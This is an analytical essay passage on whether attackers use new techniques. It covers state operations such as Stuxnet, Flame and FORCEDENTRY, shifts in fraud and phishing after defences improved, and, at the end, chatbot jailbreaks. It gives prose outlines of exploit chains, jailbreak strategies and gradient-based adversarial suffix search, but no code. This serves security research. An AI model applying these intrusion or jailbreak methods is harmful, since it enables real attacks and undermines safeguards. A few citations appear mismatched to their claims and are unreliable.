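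The DAO thief received money directly, and someone who floods a website achieves their goal as soon as the site goes down. Log4Shell let criminals install ransomware or use victims' computers to mine cryptocurrency. Birsan's first imitators could earn money legally, because companies were offering bounties for exactly what they were doing. The fragments of memory that Spectre yields are rarely of such direct use to an attacker.

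These traits are drawn from a handful of attacks that people remember because they spread. Nobody has a full list of new attack classes that includes the ones that didn't spread, so we can't calculate how often a class with all four traits does. The traits also depend on an attack's targets, which can change or be overlooked. In August 2016, a careful analyst might have rated JNDI injection a moderate danger because vulnerable lookups seemed scattered and hard to find. But Log4j's public code had already included the feature that made JNDI injection one of the worst attacks of the decade for three years by then.

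## When do governments and spyware makers use new techniques?

The attacks that spread quickly did so because many people could use them. Governments and the companies that sell them spyware often want to get into a few chosen devices by a method nobody else knows about. They are behind some of the most inventive attacks on record, but also behind many intrusions that took only an old flaw and a stolen password.

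Four operations are especially well known for their inventiveness, although much of each one was familiar:

| Operation | Main target | Known use before discovery | Most unusual part | Degree of novelty |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stuxnet | Uranium centrifuges in Iran | 1 to 2.5 years | Sabotage through industrial controllers, hidden from the engineers | Arguably a new attack class |
| Flame | Selected computers, mostly in Iran | About 2 years | A forged Microsoft certificate | New technique |
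| FORCEDENTRY | iPhones of activists and others | About 7 months | A computer built out of drawing commands | New technique |
| Operation Triangulation | iPhones of Kaspersky staff and diplomats in Russia | About 4 years | Undocumented hardware in Apple's chips | New instance of an obscure class |

### Stuxnet

Stuxnet was a worm that sabotaged the centrifuges Iran used to enrich uranium at Natanz. A Belarusian antivirus company found it in June 2010. The oldest copy known at the time dated from June 2009, but Symantec later identified an earlier version that someone had uploaded to a malware-scanning site in November 2007.

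The equipment at Natanz was not connected to the internet, so Stuxnet spread on USB sticks and across local networks. It used four Windows zero-days, an extraordinary number for one piece of malware. But according to Symantec's *W32.Stuxnet Dossier* (Falliere, O Murchu and Chien, 2011), a criminal trojan had already used one of the flaws in 2008, and a security magazine had published details of another in April 2009.

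The new part came after the break-in. Engineers program Siemens industrial controllers with a Windows program called Step 7, which uses a library file to read and write the controller's code. Falliere and colleagues describe the attack on the centrifuges' motors as follows:

1. Stuxnet replaced the library file with its own version. This version added Stuxnet's code to the controller, and left that code out whenever an engineer asked to see what the controller was running.
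2. The added code checked that the controller was connected to at least 33 motor drives from either of two manufacturers, one Finnish and one Iranian. Elsewhere it did nothing.
3. It watched the drives for about two weeks to confirm that they were running at between 807 and 1,210 hertz.
4. It raised the frequency to 1,410 hertz for 15 minutes, then returned it to normal. About four weeks later it lowered the frequency to 2 hertz for 50 minutes.

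A second attack in the same worm closed valves to raise the pressure inside the centrifuges. Ralph Langner, a specialist in industrial control systems, explains in *To Kill a Centrifuge* (2013) that the attack first recorded 21 seconds of normal sensor readings, then played them to the operators in a loop while the pressure rose.

The attackers behind Stuxnet could have got onto a Windows computer at Natanz by an ordinary route, but no ordinary tool would have broken centrifuges while the control room showed nothing wrong. Zetter (2012) reports in *Meet 'Flame,' The Massive Spy Malware Infiltrating Iranian Computers* that Stuxnet is widely believed to have severely disrupted Iran's nuclear programme in 2009 and 2010. The exact damage is uncertain.

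Whether Stuxnet used a new attack class depends on how broadly one defines the class. Specialists already knew that software could destroy machinery, because an American government laboratory had wrecked a diesel generator in 2007 by sending it commands. But nobody had publicly documented an attack that reprogrammed a controller and hid the change from its operators. Stuxnet is the strongest candidate of the four for a new class, and defenders learned of that class from the attack itself.

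### Flame

Flame was a spying program that recorded keystrokes, Skype calls and microphone audio. Researchers announced its discovery in May 2012, and Kaspersky dated its use to at least March 2010. BBC's *Flame* reports more than 600 targets. Most were in Iran, where the operators were looking for technical drawings.

Kaspersky took a module in the 2009 version of Stuxnet, which was missing from the 2010 version, as proof that the software platforms behind Stuxnet and Flame were connected, according to Zawya (2012). Fillinger and Stevens, in *Reverse-engineering of the cryptanalytic attack used in the Flame super-malware*, cite a Washington Post article in which unnamed officials attributed Flame to the United States and Israel.

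Flame could spread by posing as Windows Update. An infected computer got other computers on the local network to send their update traffic through it, then sent them a copy of Flame instead of an update. Windows rejects updates without a valid signature, so the attackers needed a certificate that appeared to come from Microsoft.

They got one by exploiting a weakness in MD5, a hash function that turns any file into a 128-bit number. An authority that signs a certificate really signs its hash, so the signature also fits any other certificate with the same hash. In a *chosen-prefix collision*, the attacker starts with two different texts, P and P′, and calculates short strings C and C′ such that

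MD5(P‖C‖S) = MD5(P′‖C′‖S)

Here ‖ means "followed by", and S is any ending the two texts share. The attackers prepared a harmless certificate and a dangerous one with the same hash. They had an automated Microsoft licensing service sign the harmless one, then copied the signature onto the dangerous one.

The attackers had to predict the harmless certificate's exact contents, which was difficult because its serial number depended on how many milliseconds the server had been running. If their request arrived slightly early or late, the whole calculation was wasted. Alexander Sotirov had helped forge a certificate using an MD5 collision in a 2008 demonstration. In *Analyzing the MD5 collision in Flame*, he estimates that the Flame forgery probably cost 10 to 100 times as much.

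Fillinger and Stevens reconstructed the method from the one surviving certificate. Each collision took about 2^49.3 MD5 operations, or roughly 40,000 hours on one processor core. With 560 cores that takes three days, which a university group could manage.

The attackers needed a forged certificate only for Windows Vista and later. Microsoft's *Flame malware collision attack explained* (2012) says that on older versions, a certificate from the licensing service could sign code without a collision. Vista and later versions rejected such a certificate because it contained a field marked as critical that they could not process. The attackers used the collision to remove that field.

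The attackers behind Flame probably didn't need a new way to make a chosen-prefix collision. Marc Stevens and his colleagues had published the first one in 2007 and released their software in June 2009, eight months before the Flame collision. Their method needed about 2^44.55 operations, and the attackers' secret method needed about 27 times as many. CWI, the Dutch institute where Stevens worked, suggests that the attackers had started developing their method before the software came out (CWI, 2012). If so, they used a new technique because they already had it, as one would expect of an agency that employs researchers.

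Flame's collision was therefore a new technique within a class that had been public for years. Such cases seem to be rare. The cryptographer Matt Blaze, quoted in Network Computing, could not think of another attack outside espionage and war that used unpublished codebreaking. He would have expected intelligence agencies to be very reluctant to risk exposing such a method by putting it in malware.

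### FORCEDENTRY

The Israeli company NSO Group sells governments a spyware program called Pegasus. FORCEDENTRY was one of its ways of getting Pegasus onto an iPhone. Citizen Lab's *FORCEDENTRY NSO Group iMessage Zero-Click Exploit Captured in the Wild* (2021) describes finding it in a backup of a Saudi activist's phone. The researchers believe it had been in use since at least February 2021. Apple patched the flaw it exploited on 13 September, six days after receiving the files.

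The attack began with an iMessage attachment whose name ended in ".gif". Beer and Groß (2021), of Google's Project Zero, explain that iPhones processed such files before showing the message, to make animations loop. The software inferred a file's format from its contents rather than its name, which gave attackers access to more than 20 image decoders. The file NSO sent was a PDF containing an image in JBIG2, a 1990s format for compressing scanned documents.

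An integer overflow made the decoder's count of the symbols in the image far too small, so the decoder reserved too little memory and wrote past the end of it. The attackers had arranged the memory so that this write replaced the recorded height of the page being drawn with an enormous value. Later drawing commands could then change memory far outside the page.

At this point an attacker in a browser would normally use JavaScript to search the memory and find where everything is. JBIG2 has no programming language, but it can combine two shapes with the logical operations AND, OR, XOR and XNOR. NSO's developers applied these to single bits. An AND followed by an XOR with 1 makes a NAND gate, and any digital circuit can be built from NAND gates. The developers made enough gates for a small processor that could add and compare 64-bit numbers, and used it to search the phone's memory.

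The image decoder ran in a sandbox, so the attackers still had to escape it. Beer and Groß (2022) show that the second stage used an Apple software feature that filters lists, for example to pick out the names that begin with T. Since 2007 these filters had been able to call almost any function on the device. Apple required filters from another process to be approved before they could run, but an obscure component approved and ran every filter it received. The attackers put their filter inside that component and sent both to a process outside the sandbox.

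The second stage did not corrupt memory, so the newest defences against memory corruption had no effect on it. The security company Trellix describes the research that grew out of it as the discovery of a new bug class. However, a 2019 hacking contest had already explored how to run code through these filters, and Beer and Groß recommend the contest author's write-up as an introduction. "New technique" is probably a fairer label than "new bug class" for both stages.

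NSO's FORCEDENTRY exploit required no click. An ordinary phishing link, which NSO's customers had used in 2016, might have worked on some targets, but activists learn to distrust links and can report the ones they receive. Citizen Lab suspects that NSO developed FORCEDENTRY because BlastDoor, Apple's new protection for iMessage, had blocked an earlier no-click exploit.

NSO's later BLASTPASS attack also used an image format in an iMessage attachment, but it did not build a computer out of an image as the earlier attack had. Google Project Zero's *An analysis of the NSO BLASTPASS iMessage exploit* (2025) reports that the initial guess that NSO had repeated the technique "turned out to be completely wrong".

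### Operation Triangulation

Kaspersky (2023) discovered this campaign when it noticed suspicious traffic from several iPhones on its office Wi-Fi. The campaign dated back to at least 2019 and had targeted dozens of Kaspersky employees. *Targeting of Russian iPhone users* (Council on Foreign Relations, 2023) lists diplomatic missions in Russia among the suspected victims. The Russian security service blamed the NSA.

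Larin, Bezvershenko and Kucherin (2023) call Operation Triangulation, an attack on iPhones, the most sophisticated exploit chain they have seen. It used four zero-days. The attack began with an invisible iMessage whose attachment exploited a flaw in an undocumented font instruction from the early 1990s. An integer overflow in the kernel then let the attackers read and write all of the phone's physical memory.

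That would have been enough on most computers, but recent iPhones have a hardware protection for the most sensitive parts of kernel memory, including the tables that control which program may use which memory. To get past it, the attackers wrote their data, its destination and a checksum to certain addresses that belong to the graphics processor. The hardware then wrote the data to that destination without applying the protection.

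Nobody outside the operation has explained how the attackers knew about this feature. Larin and colleagues found no mention of the addresses in Apple's firmware or published code. They also couldn't find the table of 256 values that the checksum depends on anywhere else. The hardware specialist Hector Martin later recognised the checksum as an error-correcting code, which suggests that the feature was meant for testing the processor's cache. The attackers might have discovered the feature by experiment, but they would have had to work out many unknown details at once. They may instead have had leaked or stolen documents.

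Although very obscure, the iPhone flaw is better described as a new instance of a known attack class than as a new class. Boris Larin described a similar attack in 2019, in which he took over PlayStation disc drives through leftover, unused hardware registers. The secret protecting the iPhone flaw was much harder to learn.

The reason for using it is clearer than in Flame's case. The targets had fairly recent phones, and many were security professionals, who are among the people most likely to notice a phishing message. The attackers also deleted the attachment and other traces. The hardware trick itself may have gone undetected for less than the four years, since the 2019 infections may have relied on different exploits.

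In 2026 Kaspersky identified Coruna, the iPhone kit that ended up with thieves, as the framework used in Triangulation. *MoldyRoost* (Roshan and Stein, 2026) describes criminals who used kits from the Coruna and DarkSword families in online advertisements aimed at people in more than 47 countries. WhatsApp will require people with vulnerable iPhones to update iOS, according to The Hacker News' *WhatsApp to Force iPhone Users to Update iOS as Website-Based Malware Attacks* (2026).

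### Volt Typhoon and Salt Typhoon

Two Chinese state groups have alarmed Western governments at least as much with much simpler methods. One of them, Volt Typhoon, broke into American communications, energy, transport and water companies and kept access to some of them for at least five years. In *PRC State-Sponsored Actors Compromise and Maintain Persistent Access to U.S. Critical Infrastructure* (2024), CISA, the NSA, the FBI and allied agencies conclude that it was preparing to disrupt these services in a crisis or war.

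In the typical intrusion the agencies describe, the group studies the organisation, then enters through a router, firewall or similar device, often with a public exploit for a known flaw. It looks for an administrator's password and uses it to reach the server that manages the network's accounts. It copies that server's database of password hashes, then cracks the hashes on its own computers, after which it can log in as a member of staff.

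Inside the network, Volt Typhoon mostly uses programs that come with Windows, a practice known as *living off the land*. The group installs little for antivirus software to find, and its commands resemble an administrator's normal work. The agencies add that the group can find and use zero-days, so a lack of skill doesn't explain its use of old flaws.

Salt Typhoon spied on telephone companies, which are among the most valuable targets for a foreign intelligence service. In a joint statement in November 2024, the FBI and CISA said that Chinese hackers had stolen call records, listened to the communications of a small number of people, mostly in government or politics, and copied information that American police had requested under court orders.

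Even so, the group seems to have needed nothing new. *Countering Chinese State-Sponsored Actors Compromise of Networks Worldwide to Feed Global Espionage System* (2025), an advisory by agencies from the United States and a dozen other countries, covers activity that overlaps with Salt Typhoon's. The agencies had not seen the intruders use any zero-days. The flaws they list include one in Cisco equipment for which a patch had been available since 2018. The intruders also used the routers' own packet-capture functions to collect passwords. Cisco's security team reported in February 2025 that the intruders had logged in with valid credentials in all but one of the cases it had investigated.

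As with other espionage, the evidence of the first break-in may have been gone by the time investigators arrived. If the attackers got in with a zero-day in 2020, investigators in 2024 could wrongly conclude that they had used a stolen password.

### Who used the zero-days of 2025

Charrier and colleagues counted 90 zero-days for 2025 and could attribute only some of them. For the first time, they attributed more to commercial surveillance vendors, such as NSO, and their customers than to traditional state espionage groups.

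They attributed at least ten to groups linked to China, twice as many as in 2024 but fewer than the 12 in 2023. Financially motivated groups accounted for nine, up from five, and two of those reportedly led to ransomware. None were attributed to North Korean groups, down from five.

The surveillance vendors' lead may come partly from counting flaws instead of operations. Breaking into a modern phone often takes a chain of three or more zero-days, while one may be enough for a firewall. Vendors and states are also hard to separate, because most of the vendors' customers are governments.

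Few zero-days involve a new technique, as Stone found for 2021. Just over half of the zero-days attributed to state espionage groups targeted security products and devices at the edge of a network, where the common flaws were elementary. Surveillance vendors concentrated on phones and browsers, and Charrier and colleagues report that the vendors found new techniques for getting past recently added protections.

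### What separates the two patterns

The target's value alone can't explain the difference. A national telephone network is worth at least as much to a spy agency as an activist's iPhone, yet attackers broke into the network using old flaws and stolen passwords. As in the cost model, an attacker has no reason to pay for a new technique while a cheaper one works, even if the target is very valuable.

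The strength of the defences explains more. An updated iPhone has no administrator with a weak password, and Apple had closed several of the simpler ways in. A telephone company has thousands of devices, some too old to receive patches, and an intruder needs to break into only one. Flame is a partial exception, since published software would probably have been enough.

The need for stealth can favour either new or known techniques. On a busy company network, attackers hide best by using an employee's account and the tools that administrators use every day, which is how Volt Typhoon stayed hidden for years. A phone has no such activity to blend into, and a spy who wants to read its messages without the owner clicking on anything needs an exploit that works silently. Stuxnet's makers had to hide the real readings from engineers, who would have stopped the centrifuges if they had seen them.

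These cases also suggest that attackers choose a technique separately for each step of an attack. The makers of Triangulation used an integer overflow to reach the kernel and used their strangest method only against the one protection that the overflow couldn't defeat. Stuxnet's makers used fairly ordinary flaws to reach the controllers. Figures for initial access would list Triangulation as a font flaw in a message attachment and leave out the hardware that no defender knew about.

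## Does closing the cheap routes push attackers toward new ones?

Groups like Volt Typhoon use old flaws and stolen passwords because these still work. If better defences closed these routes, attackers might develop new ones, but under the cost model they could also switch to another familiar route, look for an easier victim, settle for a smaller prize, or give up.

Criminologists use the word *displacement* for crime that moves instead of stopping. A simple way to measure it is

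D = G / F

where F is the fall in losses on the route that defenders closed, and G is the rise elsewhere that the closure caused. If D is 0, the attackers gave up, and if D is 1, they made up everything they lost. F is fairly easy to measure. G is not, because losses on other routes might have risen anyway.

### Chip cards

Payment cards have the longest record. A magnetic stripe provides the same data for every payment, so anyone who copies it has a working card. A chip produces a different code for each payment, and a PIN stops most thieves from using a stolen card in a shop. Britain rolled out chip and PIN from 2003 to 2006, according to lecture slides from the University of Cambridge (2020).

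The chip cards reduced the kinds of fraud they were designed to prevent. Losses at UK retailers fell by 67% between 2004 and 2009, and losses from cards intercepted in the post fell by 91%, according to Electronic Payments International. But total card fraud rose from £504.7 million in 2004 to about £610 million in 2008. Criminals had moved to payments that didn't use the chip, and more than half of the 2008 losses came from stolen card numbers used online, by phone or by post. American Banker's *Losses Mount As Fraudsters Evade UK Chip Card Protections* explains that criminals also kept copying the magnetic stripe, which British banks still had to put on every card. The copies worked in countries that had not adopted chips.

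Ross Anderson, a professor of security engineering at Cambridge, compared the change to a bulldozer crossing the landscape, "diverting flows of wickedness but not damming them". That description fit 2008, but total card fraud then fell by 28% in a single year. Card use had also grown, so even at the 2008 peak, fraud losses were a smaller share of spending than in 2004. The Global Treasurer's *2008 Fraud Figures Highlight Chip and PIN Impact* puts them at 0.12%, down from 0.14%.

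The United States adopted chips later and more abruptly. *Changes in U.S. Payments Fraud from 2012 to 2016* (Gerdes, Greene and Liu, 2018) reports that chip payments rose from 3.2% to 26.4% of the value of in-person card payments between 2015 and 2016. In-person fraud fell from $3.68 billion to $2.91 billion, while remote fraud rose from $3.40 billion to $4.57 billion. If chips caused the whole rise in remote fraud, D is 1.17 / 0.77, or about 1.5, and criminals more than made up their losses. But online shopping was also growing, and fraud hardly changed as a share of all card spending, so the true D is probably lower. Two years of data aren't enough to estimate how much lower.

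UK Finance's *Annual Fraud Report 2026* (2026) shows what happened after other countries adopted chips and banks began to protect online payments as well:

| UK card fraud | 2016 | 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| Losses from counterfeit cards | £36.9 million | £4.7 million |
| Losses from remote purchases | £432.3 million | £423.5 million |
| Number of remote purchase cases | 1.44 million | 3.20 million |
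| Average loss per remote purchase case | £300 | £132 |
| All card fraud as a share of spending | 0.084% | 0.057% |

Many online payments now require a one-time passcode sent to the customer. Criminals get past this by tricking customers into revealing the code. They have to commit fraud on more than twice as many cards as in 2016 to steal about the same amount.

Other criminals persuade people to send the money themselves. Losses from these scams rose from £420.7 million in 2020 to £576.4 million in 2025, and the type of scam changed. In 2020 more than half of losses came from diverting a genuine payment, for example with a false invoice or a call from a fake bank employee. By 2025 that share was under a quarter. Banks now check whether the name on an account matches the one the customer typed, which helps against a diverted payment but not against a fake investment, where the victim intends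 to pay the criminal's account. Losses from fake investments rose by 35% in 2025.

The total fraud that UK Finance counts rose by only 6% between 2020 and 2025, which is less than inflation. None of the replacement methods was a new kind of attack, and confidence tricks are much older than payment cards.

### Office macros

A macro is a small program inside a document. For years, criminals emailed Word and Excel files containing malicious macros and persuaded recipients to click the button that let the macros run. In October 2021 and February 2022, Microsoft announced that Office would block two kinds of macro by default.

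For the more common kind, the block depends on a label that Windows attaches to files from the internet. Criminals got around the block by putting the document inside a container, such as a disk image or a compressed archive. Windows labeled the container but not the document inside. Criminals could also replace the document with a Windows shortcut that started the malware directly.

Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* (2022) counted email campaigns from October 2021 to June 2022. Campaigns with macro attachments fell by about 66%, while those with containers or shortcuts rose by nearly 175%. The percentages have different bases, so they don't show whether criminals fully replaced the lost campaigns. If 100 campaigns used macros at the start, the fall removed 66. A 175% rise would make up for that only if about 38 campaigns already used containers or shortcuts.

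Criminals made much of the move before the block was fully in place. Microsoft suspended the rollout in early July 2022, after Proofpoint's count had ended, and resumed it later. Criminals apparently reacted to the announcement, and they had little to invent. The security firm Outflank had demonstrated the container trick in 2020, according to Cybersecurity Dive. Among several such changes, the Irish government's cyber security centre saw criminals sending malware as replies within existing email conversations, where recipients are less suspicious (NCSC Ireland, 2022).

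### Logins that need more than a password

*Multi-factor authentication* requires a second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone. Microsoft's *Extortion and ransomware drive over half of cyberattacks* (2025) credits it with blocking over 99% of attacks on people's accounts. But most of these attacks are crude. Help Net Security's *What Microsoft’s 2025 report reveals about the new rules of engagement* reports that more than 97% consist of guessing passwords, and a defence could stop all of those without stopping a more careful attacker.

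Careful attackers have found at least three ways round it. The first is to steal the *session token*, a piece of data that a website gives the browser after login so that the user doesn't have to log in again on every page. The attacker sets up a fake site that forwards everything the victim types, including the code from their phone, to the real site. The real site sends back a token, which the fake site keeps. The attacker can then use the account without logging in.

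Criminals can rent this as a service. Okta's *Tycoon 2FA phishing actors disperse, branch into new attacks* follows one popular kit, Tycoon 2FA. Okta detected the kit in 11,199 phishing attempts against a group of its customers in July 2025, and in 885 in the month before police and Microsoft took the service down on 4 March 2026. The number rose in the weeks after the takedown. According to KnowBe4's *Device Code Phishing is Surging*, the kit returned within weeks with a second method added.

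That second method abuses a login system for devices that lack a convenient keyboard, such as televisions and printers. The device shows a code, and its owner types the code into a website on a phone or computer. In *device-code phishing*, the attacker requests a code and sends it to the victim with some excuse for entering it. The victim enters it on the genuine website, passes every check, and unknowingly logs the attacker in. Microsoft notes that the victim never reveals a password. ThaiCERT's *Alert* (2026) cites a finding by the company Push Security that the number of web pages using this trick grew about 37.5 times in early 2026.

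Of the methods criminals adopted in these cases, device-code phishing was probably the closest to being new to defenders. But RFC 8628, the internet standard that defines the login system, included a warning about this attack in 2019.

The third way is to telephone someone. Some groups call a company's IT help desk, pretend to be an employee who has lost a phone, and ask for a login reset. In Mandiant's investigations, email phishing fell from 22% of intrusions in 2022 to 6% in 2025, which Kutscher attributes to better automated filters. Voice phishing reached 11%, so its growth offset at most 11 of the 16 percentage points that email lost. Kovacs (2026) reports in *Initial Access Handoff Shrinks From Hours to 22 Seconds* that voice phishing was the most common way into cloud services, at 23%, compared with 15% for email. These are shares of a changing total, so they can't show whether the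 number of phishing victims went up or down.

### Browsers and phones

The attackers in the cases so far were mostly criminals who wanted money and didn't care who it came from. Spyware makers and governments have fewer alternatives when a phone or browser becomes harder to attack, so they should be more likely to develop new kinds of attack.

Charrier and colleagues counted 90 zero-days for 2025, of which less than 10% were in browsers, far below the share in 2021 and 2022. They think browser makers' defences are working, but that attackers have also become better at hiding. Operating systems accounted for 39, up from 31 in 2024. Zero-days in phone systems rose from nine to 15, partly because several attacks needed three or more zero-days chained together.

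The 2025 attacks that escaped a browser's sandbox exploited flaws in the operating system or in the software that controls the graphics chip, not in the sandbox's own code. Most of these flaws were familiar memory errors, and only the Android notification attack might belong to a new class.

Some attackers settled for less than full control of a phone. Between July 2024 and February 2025, someone uploaded several malicious photographs to a malware-scanning site. The photographs exploited a memory error in a Samsung component that scans the pictures on a phone. Taking over the whole phone would have required more flaws, but this component could already read every photo and video on it, which may be enough for a spy.

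The Samsung attack also used a method that exists because of an earlier defence. Processors and operating systems stopped running anything stored in memory meant for data, which blocks simple exploits like the one lc described for a login program. Attackers responded by stringing together fragments of code that the victim's program already contained. Hovav Shacham described a general form of this method in *The Geometry of Innocent Flesh on the Bone* (2007), and the Samsung attackers used a variant. The defence led to a new technique, which spread to nearly everyone who exploits memory errors, but the underlying bugs were still the familiar overflows.

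### Safer languages on Android

Google has tried to get rid of those bugs. Around 2019 it began to favour *memory-safe* languages, such as Java and Rust, for new Android code. These languages prevent nearly all accidental memory errors. According to Google (2024), memory errors fell from 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 to 24% in 2024. Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that the share dropped below 20% in 2025.

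Google did this without rewriting most of its old code. If a vulnerability lasts λ years on average before someone finds and fixes it, the share that remains after t years is

e^(−t/λ)

If flaws last 2.5 years on average, five-year-old code has about one-seventh (e^(−2)) of the flaws it started with. Old code therefore becomes safer as long as programmers stop adding new flaws. Vander Stoep estimates that Android's Rust code has about 0.2 memory vulnerabilities per million lines, compared with roughly 1,000 in its C and C++ code. The Rust estimate is based on a single flaw, which Google caught before release.

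The total number of serious flaws reported in Android did not at first fall nearly as fast as the number of memory errors. Google (2022) gives 223 memory errors for 2019 and 85 for 2022, when they made up 36% of the total. These figures imply that other flaws roughly doubled, from about 70 to about 150. Most of the other flaws were logic errors, which tend to be less severe. In 2022, memory errors still made up 86% of the critical vulnerabilities.

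But these are flaws that somebody reported, and bug hunters may have changed what they look for even if attackers did not. Attackers do seem to have moved to the code that remained unsafe, where memory errors still occur. *The Doom of Device Drivers* (Maar, Draschbacher et al., 2025) cites a Google review of 2023 in which four of five complete takeovers of Android phones used a flaw in a graphics driver. An ordinary app can reach this driver directly, so attackers no longer had to take over a more privileged program first. Four companies supply the graphics chips for the whole Android market, so one flaw can work on many phones. Google is now working with the chip designer Arm to secure the drivers.

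If that effort succeeds, attackers still won't need anything new. Maar and colleagues examined 131 recent Android models and found 11 other types of driver that an ordinary app can reach. On 59% of the models, at least one of these drivers had a publicly known, highly critical flaw that the phone's maker hadn't patched. The same delay affects graphics drivers. Beer (2022) reported flaws in one whose developer had already fixed them, but phones from Google, Samsung and other makers had not yet received the fix.

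### Is displacement usually complete?

Crime prevention seems to displace less crime to other targets than criminologists once feared. In *Displacement* (1994), René Hesseling reviewed 55 studies of crime prevention and found no sign of displacement in 22 of them. In none of the 55 did displacement cancel out the whole benefit. Rob Guerette and Kate Bowers covered 102 evaluations in *Assessing the Extent of Crime Displacement and Diffusion of Benefits* (2009). They found displacement in 26% of the comparisons they could make. In 27% they found the opposite, with crime also falling beyond what the project had protected.

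There are reasons to expect more displacement in software than in physical crime. A burglar has to travel and learn a new neighbourhood, but a hacker can attack computers anywhere without travelling. When the makers of a phishing kit add a method, all their customers get it at once. Many attackers also do this for a living, so they need to replace the income when a method stops working. Criminologists mostly look for crime moving to nearby streets, and a change of method is harder to spot, so their percentages are a poor guide to how often hackers change methods.

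The card figures still suggest that displacement is incomplete over a decade or two, since fraud's share of card spending has shrunk. Over a year or two it can look complete, as it did in Britain in 2008. For macros, logins and phone exploits, nobody has published the figures needed to calculate D, so we know that many attackers moved but not how many stopped.

### How often was the next route new?

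| What defenders hardened | Where attackers went | How new it was |
|---|---|---|
| Card payments in shops | Online payments, copied stripes abroad | Familiar |
| Online card payments | Tricking customers out of passcodes | Familiar |
| Office macros | Containers and shortcuts | Public since at least 2020 |
| Password logins | Session tokens, device codes | Known classes, with device codes new to many defenders |
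| Email | Telephone calls | Familiar |
| Browsers | Operating systems and graphics drivers | Mostly familiar, with one possible new class |
| Android's privileged programs | Graphics drivers | Familiar |

In all seven cases, attackers moved mainly to familiar methods, and at most one exploit belonged to a new class. Seven cases is a small sample, and I chose them because before-and-after figures exist, so the sample favours large criminal markets over secret operations. New techniques were more common against the best-defended devices. For example, the FORCEDENTRY exploit probably came after Apple closed an easier route into iMessage.

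All seven also had a familiar alternative available, so they don't show what attackers do when there is none. That situation is rare. Suppose a company has 100 familiar weak points, and each has a 95% chance of being secure, independently of the others. The chance that all of them are secure is 0.95^100, or about 0.6%. With only 20 weak points, the chance is 36%, which is one reason a single phone, which has fewer weak points, is easier to defend than a company.

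If a target has no familiar weakness left, most criminals will go elsewhere. An attacker who wants that target has to develop something new, settle for less, or give up. Successful attacks should then become rarer, but a larger share of them should be new. If 1,000 familiar attacks and two new ones succeed in a year, new attacks make up 0.2% of the total. If defenders then stop all but one of the familiar attacks, and attackers invent nothing more, the two new attacks make up two-thirds of the total.

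## Do people who attack chatbots use simple prompts or computed ones?

Most people who attack chatbots type ordinary sentences, even though researchers have spent years developing mathematical attacks on AI models. In this they seem to behave much like people who break into companies, and a sceptic can take this as a sign that AI follows the same pattern as software. The strength of this evidence depends on why attackers keep to simple prompts and whether anyone would notice if they used something else.

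### Two ways to make a jailbreak

A *jailbreak* is an input that gets an AI model to do what its developers trained it to refuse. People write many jailbreaks by hand. *ChatGPT as a Surveillance Assistant* (2026) lists common strategies, such as giving the model an unrestricted persona, setting the request in a story, or claiming that the usual rules don't apply. Ordinary persuasion helps too, and more capable models can be more susceptible to it than weaker ones. These prompts work partly because training gives a model aims that can conflict, such as following instructions and refusing harmful requests. Safety training also may not cover everything the model can do. A model that can read a cipher may answer a question written in cipher that it would refuse in English.

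A program can also compute a jailbreak. It adds a string of text to a forbidden request, tries many changes to the string, and keeps the ones that bring the model closer to answering. The final string can look like gibberish.

The best-known programs use gradients. A gradient measures how much a small change in each part of the input would change the output. Let x be the request, s the added string, and y the opening words of an answer that complies. The program looks for the s that maximises

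P(y | x, s)

which is the probability that the model begins its answer with y. It repeats two steps, which *Evaluating the Robustness of a Production Malware Detection System* (2025) describes. First it uses the gradient to pick out promising changes, then it tests a number of them and keeps the best.

The gradient greatly reduces the number of replacements an attacker has to test. Models process text as *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words. If a model has a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, there are 640,000 ways to replace one token in a string of 20. The standard method tests only 512 of them at each step, but it still takes 500 steps, or 256,000 tests in all (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025, *The Attacker Moves Second*).

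An attacker needs a model's internal parameters to compute a gradient, and most companies that sell access to chatbots keep those parameters secret. The attacker can instead compute a string on a public model and hope it also works on the company's model. The attacker can also work without gradients, by making random changes and keeping whatever works.

### Where the claim comes from

The claim that attackers don't bother to compute their attacks comes from *Real Attackers Don't Compute Gradients* (Apruzzese, Anderson and colleagues, 2022). The paper came out a month after ChatGPT, and its evidence is about systems that detect phishing and spam. The idea grew out of a research seminar in July 2022, where people from industry kept remarking that "real attackers guess".

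Apruzzese and colleagues first searched the AI Incident Database, a public collection of AI failures, and found no case that involved gradients. A security company then gave them data from a phishing detector in commercial use. In July 2022 the detector gave uncertain results for some 9,000 phishing pages. Most of these were unlike anything in its training data. The researchers examined 100 other pages by hand and found that the attackers had used tricks like cropping, masking or stretching a company's logo.

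They also studied a 2021 contest to get phishing pages past a detector in as few attempts as possible. The winning team needed 320 attempts and the third-placed team 608, and both relied only on what they knew about phishing. Computing an attack can be difficult in practice. Facebook's spam filter, for example, has several layers, the first of which block anyone who sends large numbers of test messages, and its verdict is not immediate, so a program that learns from each attempt would get little feedback.

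The phishing pages are decent evidence that simple tricks work, but weaker evidence that attackers use nothing else. They came from a set of pages that the detector could not classify confidently. A page that a program had optimised well would not have been in that set, because the detector would have confidently classified it as harmless. In their slides, Apruzzese and colleagues answer the question of whether real attackers compute gradients with "We cannot prove it (yet)."

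Later work supports the general picture but doesn't settle the matter. Grosse, Bieringer and colleagues surveyed 271 people who work with AI in industry for *Towards More Practical Threat Models in Artificial Intelligence Security* (2023). They found that academic attacks often assume more access than outsiders have, such as to training data or a large number of queries. *A No-Defense Defense Against Gradient-Based Adversarial Attacks on ML-NIDS* (May 2026) repeated that there was no concrete evidence of anyone using gradients to evade an intrusion detector, but it cited Apruzzese and colleagues for this and reported no new search.

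If such attacks are rare, most companies may be right to ignore them. *You Don't Need Robust Machine Learning to Manage Adversarial Attack Risks* (Raff, Benaroch and Farris, 2023) considers a model that is right 95% of the time on normal inputs, where attacks make up 1% of all inputs. Hardening a model against attacks usually makes it less accurate. If every attack succeeds on the ordinary model, hardening is worthwhile only if it lowers accuracy by less than 0.95 percentage points. This calculation assumes that a successful attack does no more harm than an ordinary mistake. That may be true of a spam filter, but not of a chatbot that could help someone make a weapon.

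### What people try on chatbots

A Microsoft team attacks the company's own AI products to find weaknesses, which is called *red-teaming*. After testing more than 100 products, Bullwinkel, Minnich and colleagues (2025) concluded in *Lessons From Red Teaming 100 Generative AI Products* that basic methods often work as well as gradient-based attacks, and sometimes better. One model usually refused illegal requests that the team typed, but often complied when it put the same instructions on a picture.

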